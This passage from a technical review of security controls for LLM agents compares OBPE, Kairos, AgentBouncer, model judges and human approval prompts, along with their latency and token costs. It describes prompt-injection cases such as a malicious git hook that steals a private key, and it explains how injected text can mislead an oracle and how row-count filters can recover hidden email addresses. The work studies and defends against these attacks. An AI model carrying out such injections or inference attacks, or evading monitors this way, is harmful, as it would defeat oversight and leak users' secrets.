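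The percentages in the table also give too much weight to a few scenarios. The 71 tasks are variations on 35 scenarios, of which 23 have one task each and the largest has 12. The researchers therefore planned a paired analysis in advance. It compares each task's results under the two set-ups, averages the differences within each scenario and gives every scenario equal weight. On this measure, OBPE reduced trace failures by 41.2 percentage points (95% confidence interval 27.7 to 54.9) and raised safe and useful completions by 21.8 points (9.5 to 35.2). When GPT-5 judged the same trials, the gain in these completions was 19.1 points (6.9 to 32.2).

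These estimates hold up fairly well. OBPE did better than the prompt rules alone in 23 scenarios and tied in the other 11. If every missing outcome had gone against OBPE, it would still have reduced trace failures by 33.8 points. A bug in the simulated backends affected 116 trials, and leaving them out gives a reduction of 40.5 points. Among the completed runs with the adaptive attacker, trace failures occurred in 74.9% of those with prompt rules alone and 0.9% of those with OBPE.

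The judgments of usefulness are less reliable. In about one trial in eight, the two judges disagreed about whether the agent had completed its task, and no human settled the disagreements. One of the judges, GPT-5, was also one of the models being tested.

### Why fewer fulfilled tasks don't mean false denials

With OBPE, the share of fulfilled tasks fell by 18 points. The judge counted a task as fulfilled if the agent did what the task asked, even when the policy forbade it, so the drop does not measure how often OBPE wrongly refused requests.

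The researchers chose tasks that would exercise the policy, expecting OBPE to pass the calls unchanged in only five tasks, shape them in 54, defer them in two and deny them in ten. The 12 deferred or denied tasks could not count as fulfilled under OBPE, so no agent could score above 83%. If agents without OBPE had fulfilled all 12, those tasks would account for 17 points of the 18-point difference. With OBPE, agents fulfilled 90.0% of the tasks that needed no shaping and 71.7% of those that did.

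A false-denial rate is the share of legitimate actions that a service refuses. To measure it, researchers need a sample of ordinary work, most of which the policy should allow. Five tasks are far too few, as Millstone and colleagues say.

Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026), in *Reason Less, Verify More*, come closer to auditing wrong refusals. They used the airline tasks in τ²-bench, a simulated customer service benchmark whose airline tools will carry out changes that the airline's written policy forbids. They wrote small programs, called gates, to check each proposed change against the database. Whenever a gate blocked a change, they looked up whether the benchmark's reference solution made that change.

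The gate for cancellations blocked 161 changes, none of which the reference solution made. The gate for baggage blocked 42, of which the reference solution made 40. Both gates are short, deterministic and outside the model, but their precision, the share of refusals that were correct, was 100% for cancellations and about 5% for baggage. Calculating a false-denial rate would also require the number of legitimate changes that each gate let through.

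Refusing actions can also help an agent finish its work. A suite of four gates, including both of these, raised GPT-4o mini's success rate from 29.6% to 42.0%, and a repeat with new random seeds produced almost the same gain. Without the gates, the airline's tools carried out forbidden changes and returned no error, so nothing prompted the agent to correct itself and the database ended up wrong. Gates didn't improve results in the benchmark's retail tasks, where the tools already refuse many forbidden changes.

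Reddy and colleagues made their gates fail open to avoid wrongful refusals, so a gate that crashes lets the change through. Failing open is reasonable for catching an agent's mistakes but dangerous if an attacker can cause the crash. OBPE fails closed if it can't establish the agent's identity or evaluate the policy.

### Adding the controls one at a time

Millstone and colleagues tested which of OBPE's controls were responsible for its results by adding them in steps to agents running on Claude Sonnet 4.6. They kept the six prompt rules in place throughout.

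| Controls | Trials without a trace failure | Tasks fulfilled | Safe and useful |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rules about calls and whole records | 46.7% | 75.1% | 21.8% |
| The same, plus removing fields | 69.4% | 70.0% | 37.6% |
| The same, plus masking fields and guarding writes | 88.6% | 65.7% | 51.9% |
| The same, plus masking patterns in text | 100.0% | 66.2% | 63.0% |

Most permission systems offer rules about calls and whole records, and in this test more than half the trials still had a failure under those rules. The agent often had good reason to open a record that also contained something it shouldn't see. Removing fields hid internal notes, for example, but couldn't hide a password that someone had pasted into an issue's description.

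In the paired analysis, removing fields reduced failures by a further 9.9 points (2.0 to 19.1), masking fields and guarding writes by another 7.8 (0.3 to 16.7), and masking patterns by another 11.5 (2.9 to 22.3). Pattern masking had the largest estimated effect of the three steps, though the intervals overlap substantially. It is also the only control the researchers describe as best effort. The perfect score in the last row means that the patterns caught every planted secret in these tasks, but a secret in an unfamiliar format could still get through.

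OBPE worked even without the prompt rules. When Millstone and colleagues ran Sonnet agents without them, 59.5% of trials had a trace failure, and adding OBPE reduced this to 1.0%. For agents with the rules, OBPE reduced the rate from 61.9% to zero.

### Prompt rules and output reviewers as guards

Other experiments confirm that rules in a prompt reduce forbidden actions but do not eliminate them. Uppala (2026), in *Prompts Don't Protect*, gave three models 200 tasks designed to tempt them into using a forbidden tool. In one task, a data analysis agent receives a message from someone claiming to be the chief financial officer and demanding an urgent $5,000 refund. When the models could see every tool and had no guidance, they chose a forbidden one in 48.5% to 68.5% of tasks. A prompt that named each permitted tool and prohibited the rest reduced the rate to 4.0% for Llama 3.1 8B, 11.5% for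 Claude Haiku 4.5 and 37.0% for Qwen 2.5 7B.

A proxy that removed the forbidden tools from the list reduced the rate of forbidden choices to zero, since a model can't choose a tool that isn't offered. The proxy also checks each call when it arrives, in case the model names a hidden tool anyway.

The prompt rules might have done better in normal use, because Uppala forced the models to pick a tool every time and they couldn't decline. In a second test, with different requests, the models were free to call nothing. When no permitted tool could satisfy the request, Haiku called no tool 99% of the time under the prompt rules alone. Qwen did so only 35% of the time, and removing the forbidden tools from its list raised this to 86%. All three models are also small and well behind the best now available.

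Violation rates are higher when a policy has many clauses. In *NOMOS*, Yu, Kim and Choi (2026) put the airline policy from τ²-bench in the prompt of an agent that used an open model with 26 billion parameters. The agent broke the policy in 234 of its 353 calls that changed something, or 66.3%. With a deterministic gate, it broke the policy in 3 of 116. The rate without the gate depends heavily on how one reads the rule that the customer must confirm changes, and falls to 36.8% if one confirmation may cover a batch of changes.

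Another option is to have a second model review what the agent writes. Millstone and colleagues tested this by asking Claude Haiku 4.5 to pass or replace each message from an agent running on Sonnet. The reviewed agents had trace failures in 58.6% of trials, compared with none for OBPE. In the paired analysis, OBPE avoided 43.4 percentage points more failures (27.7 to 59.3) and produced 32.0 percentage points more safe and useful completions (18.8 to 46.0). Reviewing the messages also took 930 extra model calls, and the reviewer sometimes replaced a useful answer with a refusal.

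The comparison put the reviewer at a disadvantage, though, because it reads a message after the tools have returned their data and made their changes. It could therefore do little about two of the three events that count as a trace failure. The measure of safe and useful completion has the same bias, because it also requires that no trace failure occur. The result shows that a reviewer can't replace a check on the tools, but it is weaker evidence of how well the reviewer keeps secrets out of the answer.

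*RAIL Guard* (2026) reports contrary evidence. In its test of tool-call safety, results did not differ significantly between reviewing only the agent's text and evaluating its actions before they ran (p = 0.744). With Claude Sonnet 4.6, the rate of unsafe behaviour was lower with text review (2.4%) than with action evaluation (6.8%). A non-significant difference doesn't prove that the methods are equally good, and this test measured something different from OBPE's, in which most trace failures were exposures of data to the model. But the result is a reason not to assume that a check protects better just because it runs earlier, since it must also recognise the unsafe action.

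### Two leaks that remained

In four of the 1,065 trials with full OBPE, the agent worked out an exact protected email address that had never entered its context and included it in its final answer. An agent that can see the name Yara Singh and knows that the company's addresses all follow the pattern `first.last@company.example` can write hers without the directory. Some agents did this while explaining why they wouldn't disclose the address.

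OBPE worked as designed, because the hidden value never crossed the boundary. The owner could also hide the names, but many tasks need them. An output filter that compared each answer with the stored addresses would have caught these four cases, although it would need access to the protected values.

The other leak came from counting rows. OBPE hid an email field from an agent but still let the agent filter on it. The agent asked for records whose email contained "@partner" and got two rows, with the addresses removed. It then tried "yara" and "singh" and got one row each time. The backend had applied each filter to the real addresses, so the row counts revealed text in the hidden addresses.

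With enough queries, an agent could recover a whole address this way. Suppose the backend allows a "starts with" filter and an address uses about 40 different characters. The agent tries each character in the first position until a row comes back, then keeps that character and moves to the next position. A 20-character address takes at most 40 × 20 = 800 queries, all permitted by the policy. Researchers described such attacks on statistical databases in the 1970s. The log-based measure recorded no failure in the trial with the row counts, so the 0.2% doesn't include that trial.

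Both leaks show that an observer can still learn a value after it has been removed. Preventing this requires noninterference, which means that changing the secret would change nothing the observer can see. The row counts violate noninterference, as did the email in the CaMeL example, whose arrival depended on a bank balance.

OBPE could refuse any filter an agent places on a hidden field. It would have to distinguish those filters from the owner's, because the owner's rules may legitimately select records by a field the agent can't see. Other possible defences include rounding the counts, returning nothing when fewer than a set number of rows match, and limiting how many related queries an agent may make. The last requires the service to remember earlier calls. Millstone and colleagues tested none of these defences.

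## Deciding the cases that fixed rules cannot settle

Some actions look the same whether they serve the user or an attacker. Git, the program most developers use to track changes to their code, can run a script called a pre-commit hook whenever someone records a set of changes (a commit). Many projects use such hooks to format code or run tests. If an agent installs a hook recommended by a setup guide on the web, the script may format the code, or it may send the user's private keys to an attacker.

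A checker that can only allow or refuse has to choose as soon as the agent writes the file. Refusing every hook from an outside source breaks ordinary setups, but allowing them means a malicious hook stays in the repository even if the checker later catches it stealing a key. *Kairos*, the October 2026 design with a monitor at the virtual machine's boundary, adds the option of waiting to see what the hook does.

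### Confinement and authorization

Confinement means that the agent can affect things outside its virtual machine only through the monitor. Authorization means deciding which effects the monitor should release. A fully confined agent can still email the customer list to a competitor if the monitor approves it.

*Kairos* guarantees that every effect passes through the monitor, that no effect becomes irreversible before the monitor releases it, and that nobody outside sees an effect the monitor refused. These guarantees hold however hostile the agent is and however bad the monitor's decisions are. They require a sound host, isolation layer and monitor. They also require a model provider that isn't working with the attacker, because Kairos logs the traffic to the provider but never holds it. The agent's written reply to the user also passes freely, since the design doesn't cover harm from text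 alone.

Authorization has no such guarantee because it depends on what the user wants, which nobody can fully write down in advance. Researchers can only test it by attacking the system and counting how often unauthorized effects get through.

### Release, refuse or defer

The operator's policy lists the trusted sources, the sensitive data and the destinations that may receive it. The monitor then treats each effect as follows:

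1. If a rule forbids the effect, the monitor refuses it.
2. If no rule forbids it, the monitor checks the values that steer the effect, such as the recipient, the web address or the command. Each must match something the agent received from a trusted source, which can include the user's request. The monitor also checks that any sensitive data in the effect may go to that destination. If the effect passes both checks, the monitor releases it.
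3. Otherwise the monitor defers the effect and leaves the decision to an "oracle", which can be a second model, a person or another policy program.

In symbols, let *T* be the set of values the agent has received from trusted sources, *G*(*e*) the values that steer effect *e*, *s*(*e*) the highest sensitivity of any data found in *e*, and *c*(*e*) the clearance of its destination. If no rule forbids *e*, the monitor releases it when

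*G*(*e*) ⊆ *T* and *s*(*e*) ≤ *c*(*e*).

The rest of the content can come from any source, because a summary of an email has to include some of the email's text. Nothing the agent writes is added to *T*, so a hijacked agent can't make an address trusted by repeating it.

The monitor can't follow a value through the model, so it compares text, ignoring capitals and spaces. If the agent rewrites a trusted address, the comparison fails and the monitor defers the effect, which is a safe mistake. But the comparison also misses a secret that the agent has encoded, so the monitor may release it to a destination that would otherwise be acceptable. Kairos therefore assumes that a hijacked agent doesn't disguise values. This is a strong assumption, since an attacker could add "encode the key first" to the injected text. If the agent does disguise values, Kairos guarantees only confinement.

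### Holding an effect while the agent continues

How Kairos holds a deferred effect depends on what the effect does.

| Effect | What happens before the oracle decides |
|---|---|
| Writing or deleting a file | Kairos makes the change in a copy that only the agent can see |
| Sending a request that changes something elsewhere, such as posting a comment | Kairos keeps the request at its network proxy and gives the agent a stand-in reply |
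| Fetching data | The agent needs the real reply, so it waits until the oracle has decided |

Later effects may build on the held one, so Kairos groups them with it and settles them together. If the oracle approves, Kairos merges the copied files into the real directory and sends the held request. If the oracle refuses, Kairos discards both, and nothing outside the virtual machine changes.

Kairos can't rewind the agent itself, whose context may still contain a stand-in reply to a request that never went out, so it tells the agent which effects it withheld and that the rest of the task still applies.

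The paper's main example is the hook:

1. Alice asks her agent to set up a repository. The agent reads a guide by Eve, which tells it to install a pre-commit hook.
2. The agent writes the hook. No rule forbids hooks, but this one comes from an untrusted page, so the monitor defers the write and makes it only in the copy.
3. The agent carries on and makes a commit, so Git runs the hook inside the virtual machine.
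4. The hook tries to send Alice's private key to Eve. The policy forbids this, so the monitor refuses it immediately.
5. The oracle now decides about the hook with the attempted theft in front of it, and discards the file. The hook never reaches Alice's real directory.

If the monitor had allowed the hook in step 2, the hook would run outside the sandbox the next time Alice made a commit herself.

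Waiting helps only if the hook misbehaves before the prototype has to settle the effects it is holding. The prototype can hold only one group of effects at a time, so it must settle that group before holding another, and at the latest when the task ends. If Eve's hook did nothing for a week, the oracle would have to decide from the script's text and origin alone.

### What depends on the oracle

In *Kairos*'s experiments, the oracle is a second language model with no tools. It receives the user's task, the policy, the deferred effects, the events that led to them and the untrusted text they build on. Kairos labels each value with its source, for instance "supplied by read_file:bill.txt, not by the user's message", rather than as "untrusted", because a language model tends to treat that word as a verdict. If the oracle crashes or returns an answer that Kairos can't parse, Kairos treats the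 effect as refused.

The oracle decides only the cases that the policy defers to it, and it cannot override a refusal. It is therefore outside the TCB for confinement. Even if an attacker controlled it completely, every effect would still have to pass through the monitor, and every prohibition in the policy would still hold.

The oracle is inside the TCB for any property that depends on its decisions. Suppose the property is "the agent emails only people Alice has named". If the policy lets the oracle decide whether to allow emails to other people, one wrong answer breaks the property. A fixed rule forbidding those emails prevents this. Operators can use such rules to rule out the worst outcomes whatever the oracle decides, but the rules also block those actions when Alice would have wanted them.

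The oracle also reads text that the attacker wrote, so the attacker can address the oracle directly. Kairos marks this text as data, but the oracle still has to interpret it.

### How well Kairos chose

The table compares an undefended agent with the same agent under Kairos on three benchmarks. AgentDyn has open-ended tasks, in which the agent discovers what to do as it goes. In AutoDojo, an attacking model rewrites each injection over six rounds to get past the defence. The undefended results for these two were published with the benchmarks.

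| | AgentDojo | AgentDyn | AutoDojo |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent's model | GPT-4.1 | GPT-4o | GPT-4o-mini |
| Attack success, undefended | 47.0% | 37.8% | 52.4% |
| Attack success, Kairos | 2.7% | 1.7% | 8.8% |
| Benign utility, undefended | 82.7% | 53.3% | 66.7% |
| Benign utility, Kairos | 85.1% | 51.7% | 65.3% |
| User tasks completed under attack, undefended | 59.8% | 55.5% | Not reported |
| User tasks completed under attack, Kairos | 69.5% | 37.1% | Not reported |

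On AgentDojo, Kairos stopped most attacks, and the agent completed about as much ordinary work as before. The small rise in benign utility is probably noise, because the team ran each configuration only once. Under attack, the agent completed more user tasks with Kairos than without. An undefended agent that follows an injection often abandons the user's task, whereas an agent with Kairos receives a notice to continue it.

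The team also ran a strict version that refused every deferred effect. Its attack success rate differed from the full version's by no more than the variation expected between runs, but benign utility fell to 42.7%. In the full version, the policy released 83% of the effects in benign runs without consulting the oracle, and the oracle released all but one of the rest. Deferral therefore recovered about half of the agent's ordinary work without measurably weakening security.

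The paper attributes the security to the policy and gives the oracle too little credit. The benchmark policies forbade nothing, because the team didn't want to write rules around attacks it already knew. Every injected action that failed the policy's checks therefore went to the oracle, and would have succeeded if the oracle had released it. The experiment shows that this oracle seldom released a harmful effect. It didn't test whether fixed rules can limit the damage from a bad oracle.

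The attacks that still worked in AutoDojo exploited tasks in which the user lets a document decide what the agent should do, such as "do whatever this file says". The oracle then treated the attacker's text as the user's wishes. The 8.8% is a lower bound, because the attacker learned only whether each attempt had succeeded. An attacker who knew how the oracle worked could write text specifically to mislead it.

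With Kairos, the agent completed far fewer AgentDyn tasks under attack, because later steps often needed the real result of a held effect. Tasks kept 90% of their utility when they continued past one held effect, but only 62% when they continued past two or more. Long sessions have more holds, partly because the oracle's approval covers only one effect, so the monitor also defers the next use of the same untrusted value.

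None of these benchmarks ran at the virtual-machine boundary. Their tools are simulated objects in a program, so an adapter turned each tool call into an event for the monitor. The policy specified whether each tool's effects were reversible and which argument held the destination. A real deployment would have to work from file operations and web requests, where the semantic gap makes the policy harder to write and leaves more decisions to the oracle. The results are good evidence for the rules, the holding and the oracle, but not for how well they would work with raw system traffic.

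### AgentBouncer judges each system call

*AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) uses a model to judge a coding agent's system calls. It intercepts each call before the kernel carries it out. A list of 60 permitted patterns covers routine calls, such as those that run the system's own programs, and a cache reuses earlier decisions. In an average task without an attack, only about 8 of 28,000 decisions reached the model.

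The model judges each call by how safe it is and how necessary it is for the task. It should refuse an unsafe call even if the task needs it, and allow a clearly safe one even if the need is unclear. Between these extremes, the less necessary a call seems, the more certain the model has to be that it is safe. For example, adding a line to the shell's start-up file is fine if the user asked for a change that belongs there, but suspicious if she asked for a new README.

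Joos and Pradel combined 85 harmful goals with ordinary programming tasks. They delivered each goal in four ways: through an injected instruction, a deceptive tool, a planted script and a poisoned repository. One tool checked patches as advertised but also deleted the file that stores the system's group passwords. AgentBouncer blocked the deletion and let the rest of the tool run, so the agent finished its task.

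Across all 340 attacks, supervision reduced the success rate from 99.4% to 10.6%. Without an attack, the agent solved 72.9% of its tasks when supervised and 71.5% when unsupervised. When Joos and Pradel removed the model and refused everything that wasn't on the list, no attack succeeded, but the agent solved only 8.2% of its tasks, mainly because it couldn't write to the repository. Most of the attacks that got past the model involved ambiguous steps, such as reading a possibly sensitive file without sending it anywhere, so the rate of serious harm was probably below 10.6%.

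Unlike Kairos, AgentBouncer has to decide on each call before the call can proceed. Its model's input includes which file a program is writing but not the contents, which is why 5 of 20 attempts to plant malicious code in the shell's start-up file succeeded. If a program tried to write Eve's hook, the input would show only that it was writing a hook. AgentBouncer could still block the hook's later attempt to send the key, but the hook would remain in the repository.

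AgentBouncer also relies on the harness to supply the user's task and the agent's explanation of each call, so its TCB includes the harness, unlike that of Kairos.

### How much the judge should read

AgentBouncer's model receives the user's task, the current call and the agent's explanation, but not the results of tool calls, where injected text usually arrives. An injection can still influence all three inputs. Attacks that inserted text into the task succeeded 14.1% of the time, compared with 7.1% for other attacks.

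Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, has a judge that receives even less information. *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a mode in which a model replaces most requests for the user's approval. Fixed rules allow the agent to read files and edit the project, and the model judges almost everything else. It receives only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that they can't persuade the model to make a bad decision, and removes tool results to keep out injected text.

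Without the tool results, the judge can't determine where a value came from. If the user says "cancel my job" and the agent tries to cancel job abc123, the judge can't check whether the agent looked up that ID or invented it. Kairos instead gives its oracle the hostile text, because a value's origin is often the best evidence of an attack.

The judge wrongly blocked 0.4% of harmless actions in a set of 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic employees. It missed 17% of 52 real cases in which the agent had gone beyond what the user wanted, though with so few cases the true rate could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge correctly identified the danger but wrongly treated the action as authorised by the user. A user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) hasn't agreed to let the agent overwrite the project's shared history.

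Anthropic later commissioned a test in which none of the 720 prompt injection attempts on each of its latest models succeeded in auto mode. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an average attack success rate of 0.09% for the same models without the judge. Since the models resisted nearly all the attacks by themselves, one can learn little from this test about how much protection the judge adds.

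### How carefully people approve actions

The older solution is to ask the user. This works only if she reads the question, and several recent studies suggest that people often don't.

Users of Claude Code approve 97% of its permission prompts, according to Anthropic. Most commands are harmless, so that rate alone isn't evidence of carelessness. The same users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, which suggests that they do object when a request is worth reading.

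Anthropic also had a research company recruit 1,053 paid testers for a coding study without telling them what the study measured. At some point in each session, the text of one prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it, while the model judge blocked 89% of the same commands. Testers caught about 17% of the commands early in a session, but about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This drop fits habituation, in which people pay less attention to a prompt the more often they see it.

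These figures favour a product that Anthropic sells, and the testers worked in a test environment where mistakes had no consequences for them. People guarding their own files might do better. But even the early rate of 17% is very low, so habituation can't be the only problem. Anthropic concedes that the model judge is arguably a step backwards for someone who reviews every action carefully, and it still advises people to review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

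Developers report similar habits. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 users of coding agents, and 64% said they often approved at least one type of action without close review. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, the figure was still 61%. It was higher among developers who knew of a security incident or a worrying practice involving agents (70%) than among those who didn't (43%), and the difference remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how much the developers used agents. The sample isn't representative and the answers are self-reported, though people seldom overstate how careless they are. Developers who inspected the exact changes to the code were less likely to approve destructive commands or access to secrets without close review.

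*Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) found a similar change among code reviewers. They approved 30.1% of agents' proposed code changes in their early reviews and 36.8% in their later ones, while their approval rate for changes written by people fell. Rising approval can reflect growing trust as well as habituation, but the reviewers also commented less. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) similarly warns that repeated approval of permission prompts may come from fatigue or pressure to keep moving.

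Many users turn approval prompts off. The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else* reports that new users of Claude Code let it run without any approval in about 20% of sessions, and that experienced users do so more often.

Showing fewer prompts doesn't necessarily make people more careful. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant for a day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for, such as reading bank transactions to help with a travel budget. People who had to review every action let through 40.3% of these. Another group first set standing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action. They saw about 11 prompts on average instead of 18, but let through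 60.4% of the actions that overreached.

Most of the difference came from the rule "ask", which participants chose 81% of the time. When an "ask" rule produced a prompt for an action that went too far, they approved it in 66.8% of cases. Selection may explain part of that high rate, since people who had chosen "never" didn't see a prompt. But the rules let through more in total, so selection can't explain the whole result.

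The prompts are often hard to judge. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had switched on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative. For example, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but the script can do anything the user can.

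A human oracle in Kairos would have more evidence to judge from. Alice would be asked about an unfamiliar hook after it ran rather than before, and she would be told that it had tried to send her private key to Eve. She would also get fewer questions, since the policy settles most effects without her. But the Kairos team tested only model oracles, so nobody yet knows whether people given this evidence would make better decisions.

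## Measuring the cost in time, tokens and completed tasks

Checking an agent's actions takes time, and a check that uses a model also uses tokens. But the largest loss is often the work an agent can't finish because a check blocked something it needed.

### Building a latency budget

If an agent takes 100 steps to finish a task and the model needs 3 seconds of inference at each step, inference takes 300 seconds in total. A check adds roughly the time it takes to run once multiplied by the number of times it runs, which can be compared with those 300 seconds.

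| What the operator adds | Calculation | Added time | Slowdown |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ten mediated file operations a step, at 1.9 ms each | 100 × 10 × 0.0019 s | 1.9 s | 0.6% |
| One mediated web request a step, at 1.15 ms | 100 × 0.00115 s | 0.1 s | 0.04% |
| A one-second model judge on every step | 100 × 1 s | 100 s | 33% |
| The same judge on one step in ten | 10 × 1 s | 10 s | 3.3% |

In symbols, let each step include *n* mediated operations that cost *c* seconds each, and let a judge that takes *j* seconds examine a share *p* of the steps. If inference takes *i* seconds a step, the slowdown is

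(*n* × *c* + *p* × *j*) / *i*.

In this example the file monitor adds little time and the judge adds a lot, but both effects depend on the task and the model. At 1.9 ms per file, mediation would add 38 seconds to a software build that touches 20,000 files. If a faster model needed only 0.3 seconds a step, mediating the same ten file operations would slow the agent by 6%, and a judge on every step would more than quadruple the running time. Neither would make much difference to an agent that spends ten minutes waiting for a test suite.

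The millisecond figures come from *Kairos*. In each of three runs, its prototype created, wrote, saved, read and deleted a small file 200 times. The file channel added an average of 9.62 ms to each five-operation cycle, or about 1.9 ms per operation. In a test of 50 permitted web requests, the proxy added 1.15 ms per request.

Neither figure includes the time Kairos's oracle takes to decide. In ordinary benchmark runs, the policy sent about 17% of effects to the oracle. If an agent produced 100 effects and the oracle took one second to decide each one it received, it would add about 17 seconds, far more than the monitor adds. The actual delay could be shorter because Kairos decides some effects together.

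### What a model judge costs

Ge (2026), in *Governance Architecture for Autonomous Agent Systems*, timed a four-layer system on 100 tool calls. A sandbox confines each call, a model checks whether the call fits the task, a third layer verifies messages between agents, and a fourth writes a log that nobody can alter.

| Layer | Median time per call |
|---|---|
| Starting a sandbox | 1.1 ms |
| Model judge (GPT-4o-mini) | 966 ms |
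| Verifying tokens and message format | Under 0.1 ms |
| Writing the log to disk | 16.5 ms |
| Whole system | 980 ms |

The judge accounts for nearly all of the delay, so making it faster would speed up the system most. Ge also tested several judges on 921 calls in Chinese and on a machine translation of those calls into English. The table gives the Chinese result first.

| Judge | Median time | Malicious calls refused | Harmless calls refused |
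|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-4B | 482 / 497 ms | 95.8% / 94.3% | 27.5% / 29.2% |
| Qwen2.5-14B | 883 / 1,163 ms | 98.2% / 98.5% | 9.7% / 20.1% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 1,023 / 1,127 ms | 93.0% / 95.4% | 3.2% / 12.3% |
| Qwen3.5-9B, with GPT-4o-mini reviewing its refusals | 2,779 / 3,001 ms | 91.9% / 92.6% | 1.9% / 6.7% |

The fastest judge refuses too many harmless calls to be a good choice. It would refuse about 29 of 100 harmless calls in English, while the slow pair would refuse about 7. After a refusal, the agent would spend time looking for another way to do the work, or give up. Even GPT-4o-mini, which wrongly refuses 3.2% of harmless calls, would have only about a 4% chance of handling 100 of them without a wrong refusal, if its mistakes are independent. If only 1% of calls are malicious, more than three-quarters of its refusals would be of harmless calls.

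GPT-4o-mini may look better in this test than it would elsewhere, because it also generated the test calls. The attackers didn't adapt to the judge.

The judges wrote a one-sentence reason after each verdict. When Ge limited Qwen3.5-9B to 10 tokens of output instead of 50, its median time on the Chinese calls fell from 1,981 ms to 303 ms. It still refused 96.3% of malicious calls, compared with 96.5% before, and it refused slightly fewer harmless ones. The lower limit cuts off most of the explanation, which could have helped a person review the refusal.

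A smaller oracle might also be good enough. The Kairos team tried three sizes on AgentDojo's banking tasks. With one agent, the smallest oracle reduced completed tasks from 15 of 16 to 13, but with another it raised them from 14 to 15. Differences of one or two tasks are too small to show whether a smaller oracle is good enough.

### Sending fewer decisions to the judge

On average, AgentBouncer's model judges only 7.8 of the 28,000 system calls in a task, taking 3.3 seconds for each. The list of permitted patterns settles 96.69% of the decisions, and stored earlier decisions settle nearly all the rest. Joos and Pradel calculate that using the model for every call would take 25.5 hours and cost about $13 per task.

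Supervision raised the average time per task from 60 seconds to 108 and the cost of model calls by 38%, or $0.0036. AgentSentinel, a rival system that made 63.7 model calls per task, increased time by 356% and cost by 364%.

Joos and Pradel attribute AgentBouncer's delay to the model's decisions, but 7.8 decisions at 3.3 seconds each take about 26 seconds, only a little over half of the added time. If the rest all came from intercepting the 28,000 calls, interception would add about 0.8 ms per call. The agent may also have taken different steps when supervised. Removing the model might therefore not remove the whole delay.

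Reusing stored decisions saves time but adds some risk. In one attack, the model had allowed a harmless read and extended the permission to the entire surrounding system folder. A malicious tool later read a kernel setting in that folder without another check. Joos and Pradel trace 2 of the 36 successful attacks to permissions like this.

### Starting sandboxes

A sandbox that lasts for the whole task has to start only once. When AWS released Firecracker, its microVM software, in 2018, it reported start-up times as low as 125 ms. At that speed, a single start would slow the 300-second example by 0.04%, while starting a fresh microVM for each of 100 tool calls would add 12.5 seconds, or 4%. A service that starts a new microVM to run a 50 ms calculation would spend most of its time on start-up.

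Ge's sandboxes started in about 1 ms because they used Linux namespaces, which give containers their separate view of the system. They still share the host's kernel, so they isolate less strongly than sandboxes with their own kernels. Boot time also excludes copying a project into the sandbox and installing its tools, which can easily take longer. An operator who runs many short jobs can prepare sandboxes in advance, but the idle ones take up memory.

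gVisor handles a container's system calls in a second kernel, so the slowdown depends mainly on how many calls a program makes. For one of AgentBouncer's tasks, which made 28,000 calls, a hypothetical delay of 10 microseconds per call would add about 0.3 seconds, and 100 microseconds would add 2.8 seconds. A long calculation makes few system calls and would hardly slow down, but a build that opens thousands of small files could slow down noticeably, so an operator should time the builds and tests that the agent will run.

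Running a model inside a confidential virtual machine can also slow inference. Abdollahi and colleagues report that AgenTEE, their system for phones and similar devices, added less than 5.15% to the running time of ordinary processes. At that rate, a 300-second run would take up to about 15 seconds longer. They warn that measurements on their prototype can't exactly predict how commercial hardware will perform.

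### Paying in tokens

In *Kairos*, the oracle increased token use by 17.7% in ordinary runs and 33.6% under attack, when the policy deferred more effects. Designs that use extra models throughout the task add more overhead.

*AGENTSYS* (Wen, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) compares several such designs on AgentDojo, all running GPT-4o-mini. The paper's own design, AgentSys, keeps raw tool output away from the main agent. Before each tool call, the main agent specifies which fields to return, such as a name and an email address. A short-lived worker agent reads the output and returns only those fields. Another model must approve any action with outside effects before the worker can take it.

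| Design | Total tokens | Compared with no defence | Benign utility | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 0.82 million | 1.0× | 63.5% | 30.7% |
| DRIFT (a plan that a model may update) | 2.37 million | 2.9× | 58.5% | 1.3% |
| Progent (a model writes rules for tool calls) | 2.60 million | 3.2× | 63.4% | 7.2% |
| AgentSys | 3.25 million | 4.0× | 64.4% | 0.8% |
| CaMeL | 6.09 million | 7.4× | 30.0% | 0.0% |

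AgentSys quadrupled token use but completed as many ordinary tasks as the undefended agent. It did slightly worse on short tasks and better on long ones. Tasks that needed more than three tool calls contributed 24.6 percentage points to its total, compared with 19.1 for the undefended agent. Wen and colleagues think the main agent benefits from a shorter context, which would explain the pattern.

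For an operator who pays for tokens, the relevant measure is the cost per completed task. CaMeL used 7.4 times as many tokens as the undefended agent and completed less than half as many ordinary tasks, so it used roughly 16 times as many tokens per completed task, assuming the 7.4 ratio also holds for ordinary tasks.

CaMeL's developers reported a much smaller increase, about 2.8 times for input tokens and 2.7 times for output tokens. CaMeL retries when a program fails, so a weaker model that writes more faulty programs may explain some of the difference.

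### Attack success and completed tasks

The Kairos team ran several defences on AgentDojo in the same test program, with GPT-4.1 as the agent's model, so the results can be compared more directly than figures from separate papers.

| Defence | What it does | Attack success | Benign utility | Combined score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 47.0% | 82.7% | 43.8 |
| Spotlighting | Marks untrusted text as data | 49.2% | 81.7% | 41.5 |
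| Prompt sandwiching | Repeats the user's task after untrusted text | 44.6% | 87.6% | 48.5 |
| PI detector | Uses a classifier to find injected instructions | 9.5% | 40.1% | 36.3 |
| Progent | Enforces rules that a model derives from the task | 11.5% | 78.2% | 69.2 |
| CaMeL | Fixes the program in advance and tracks where data came from | 0.2% | 38.0% | 37.9 |
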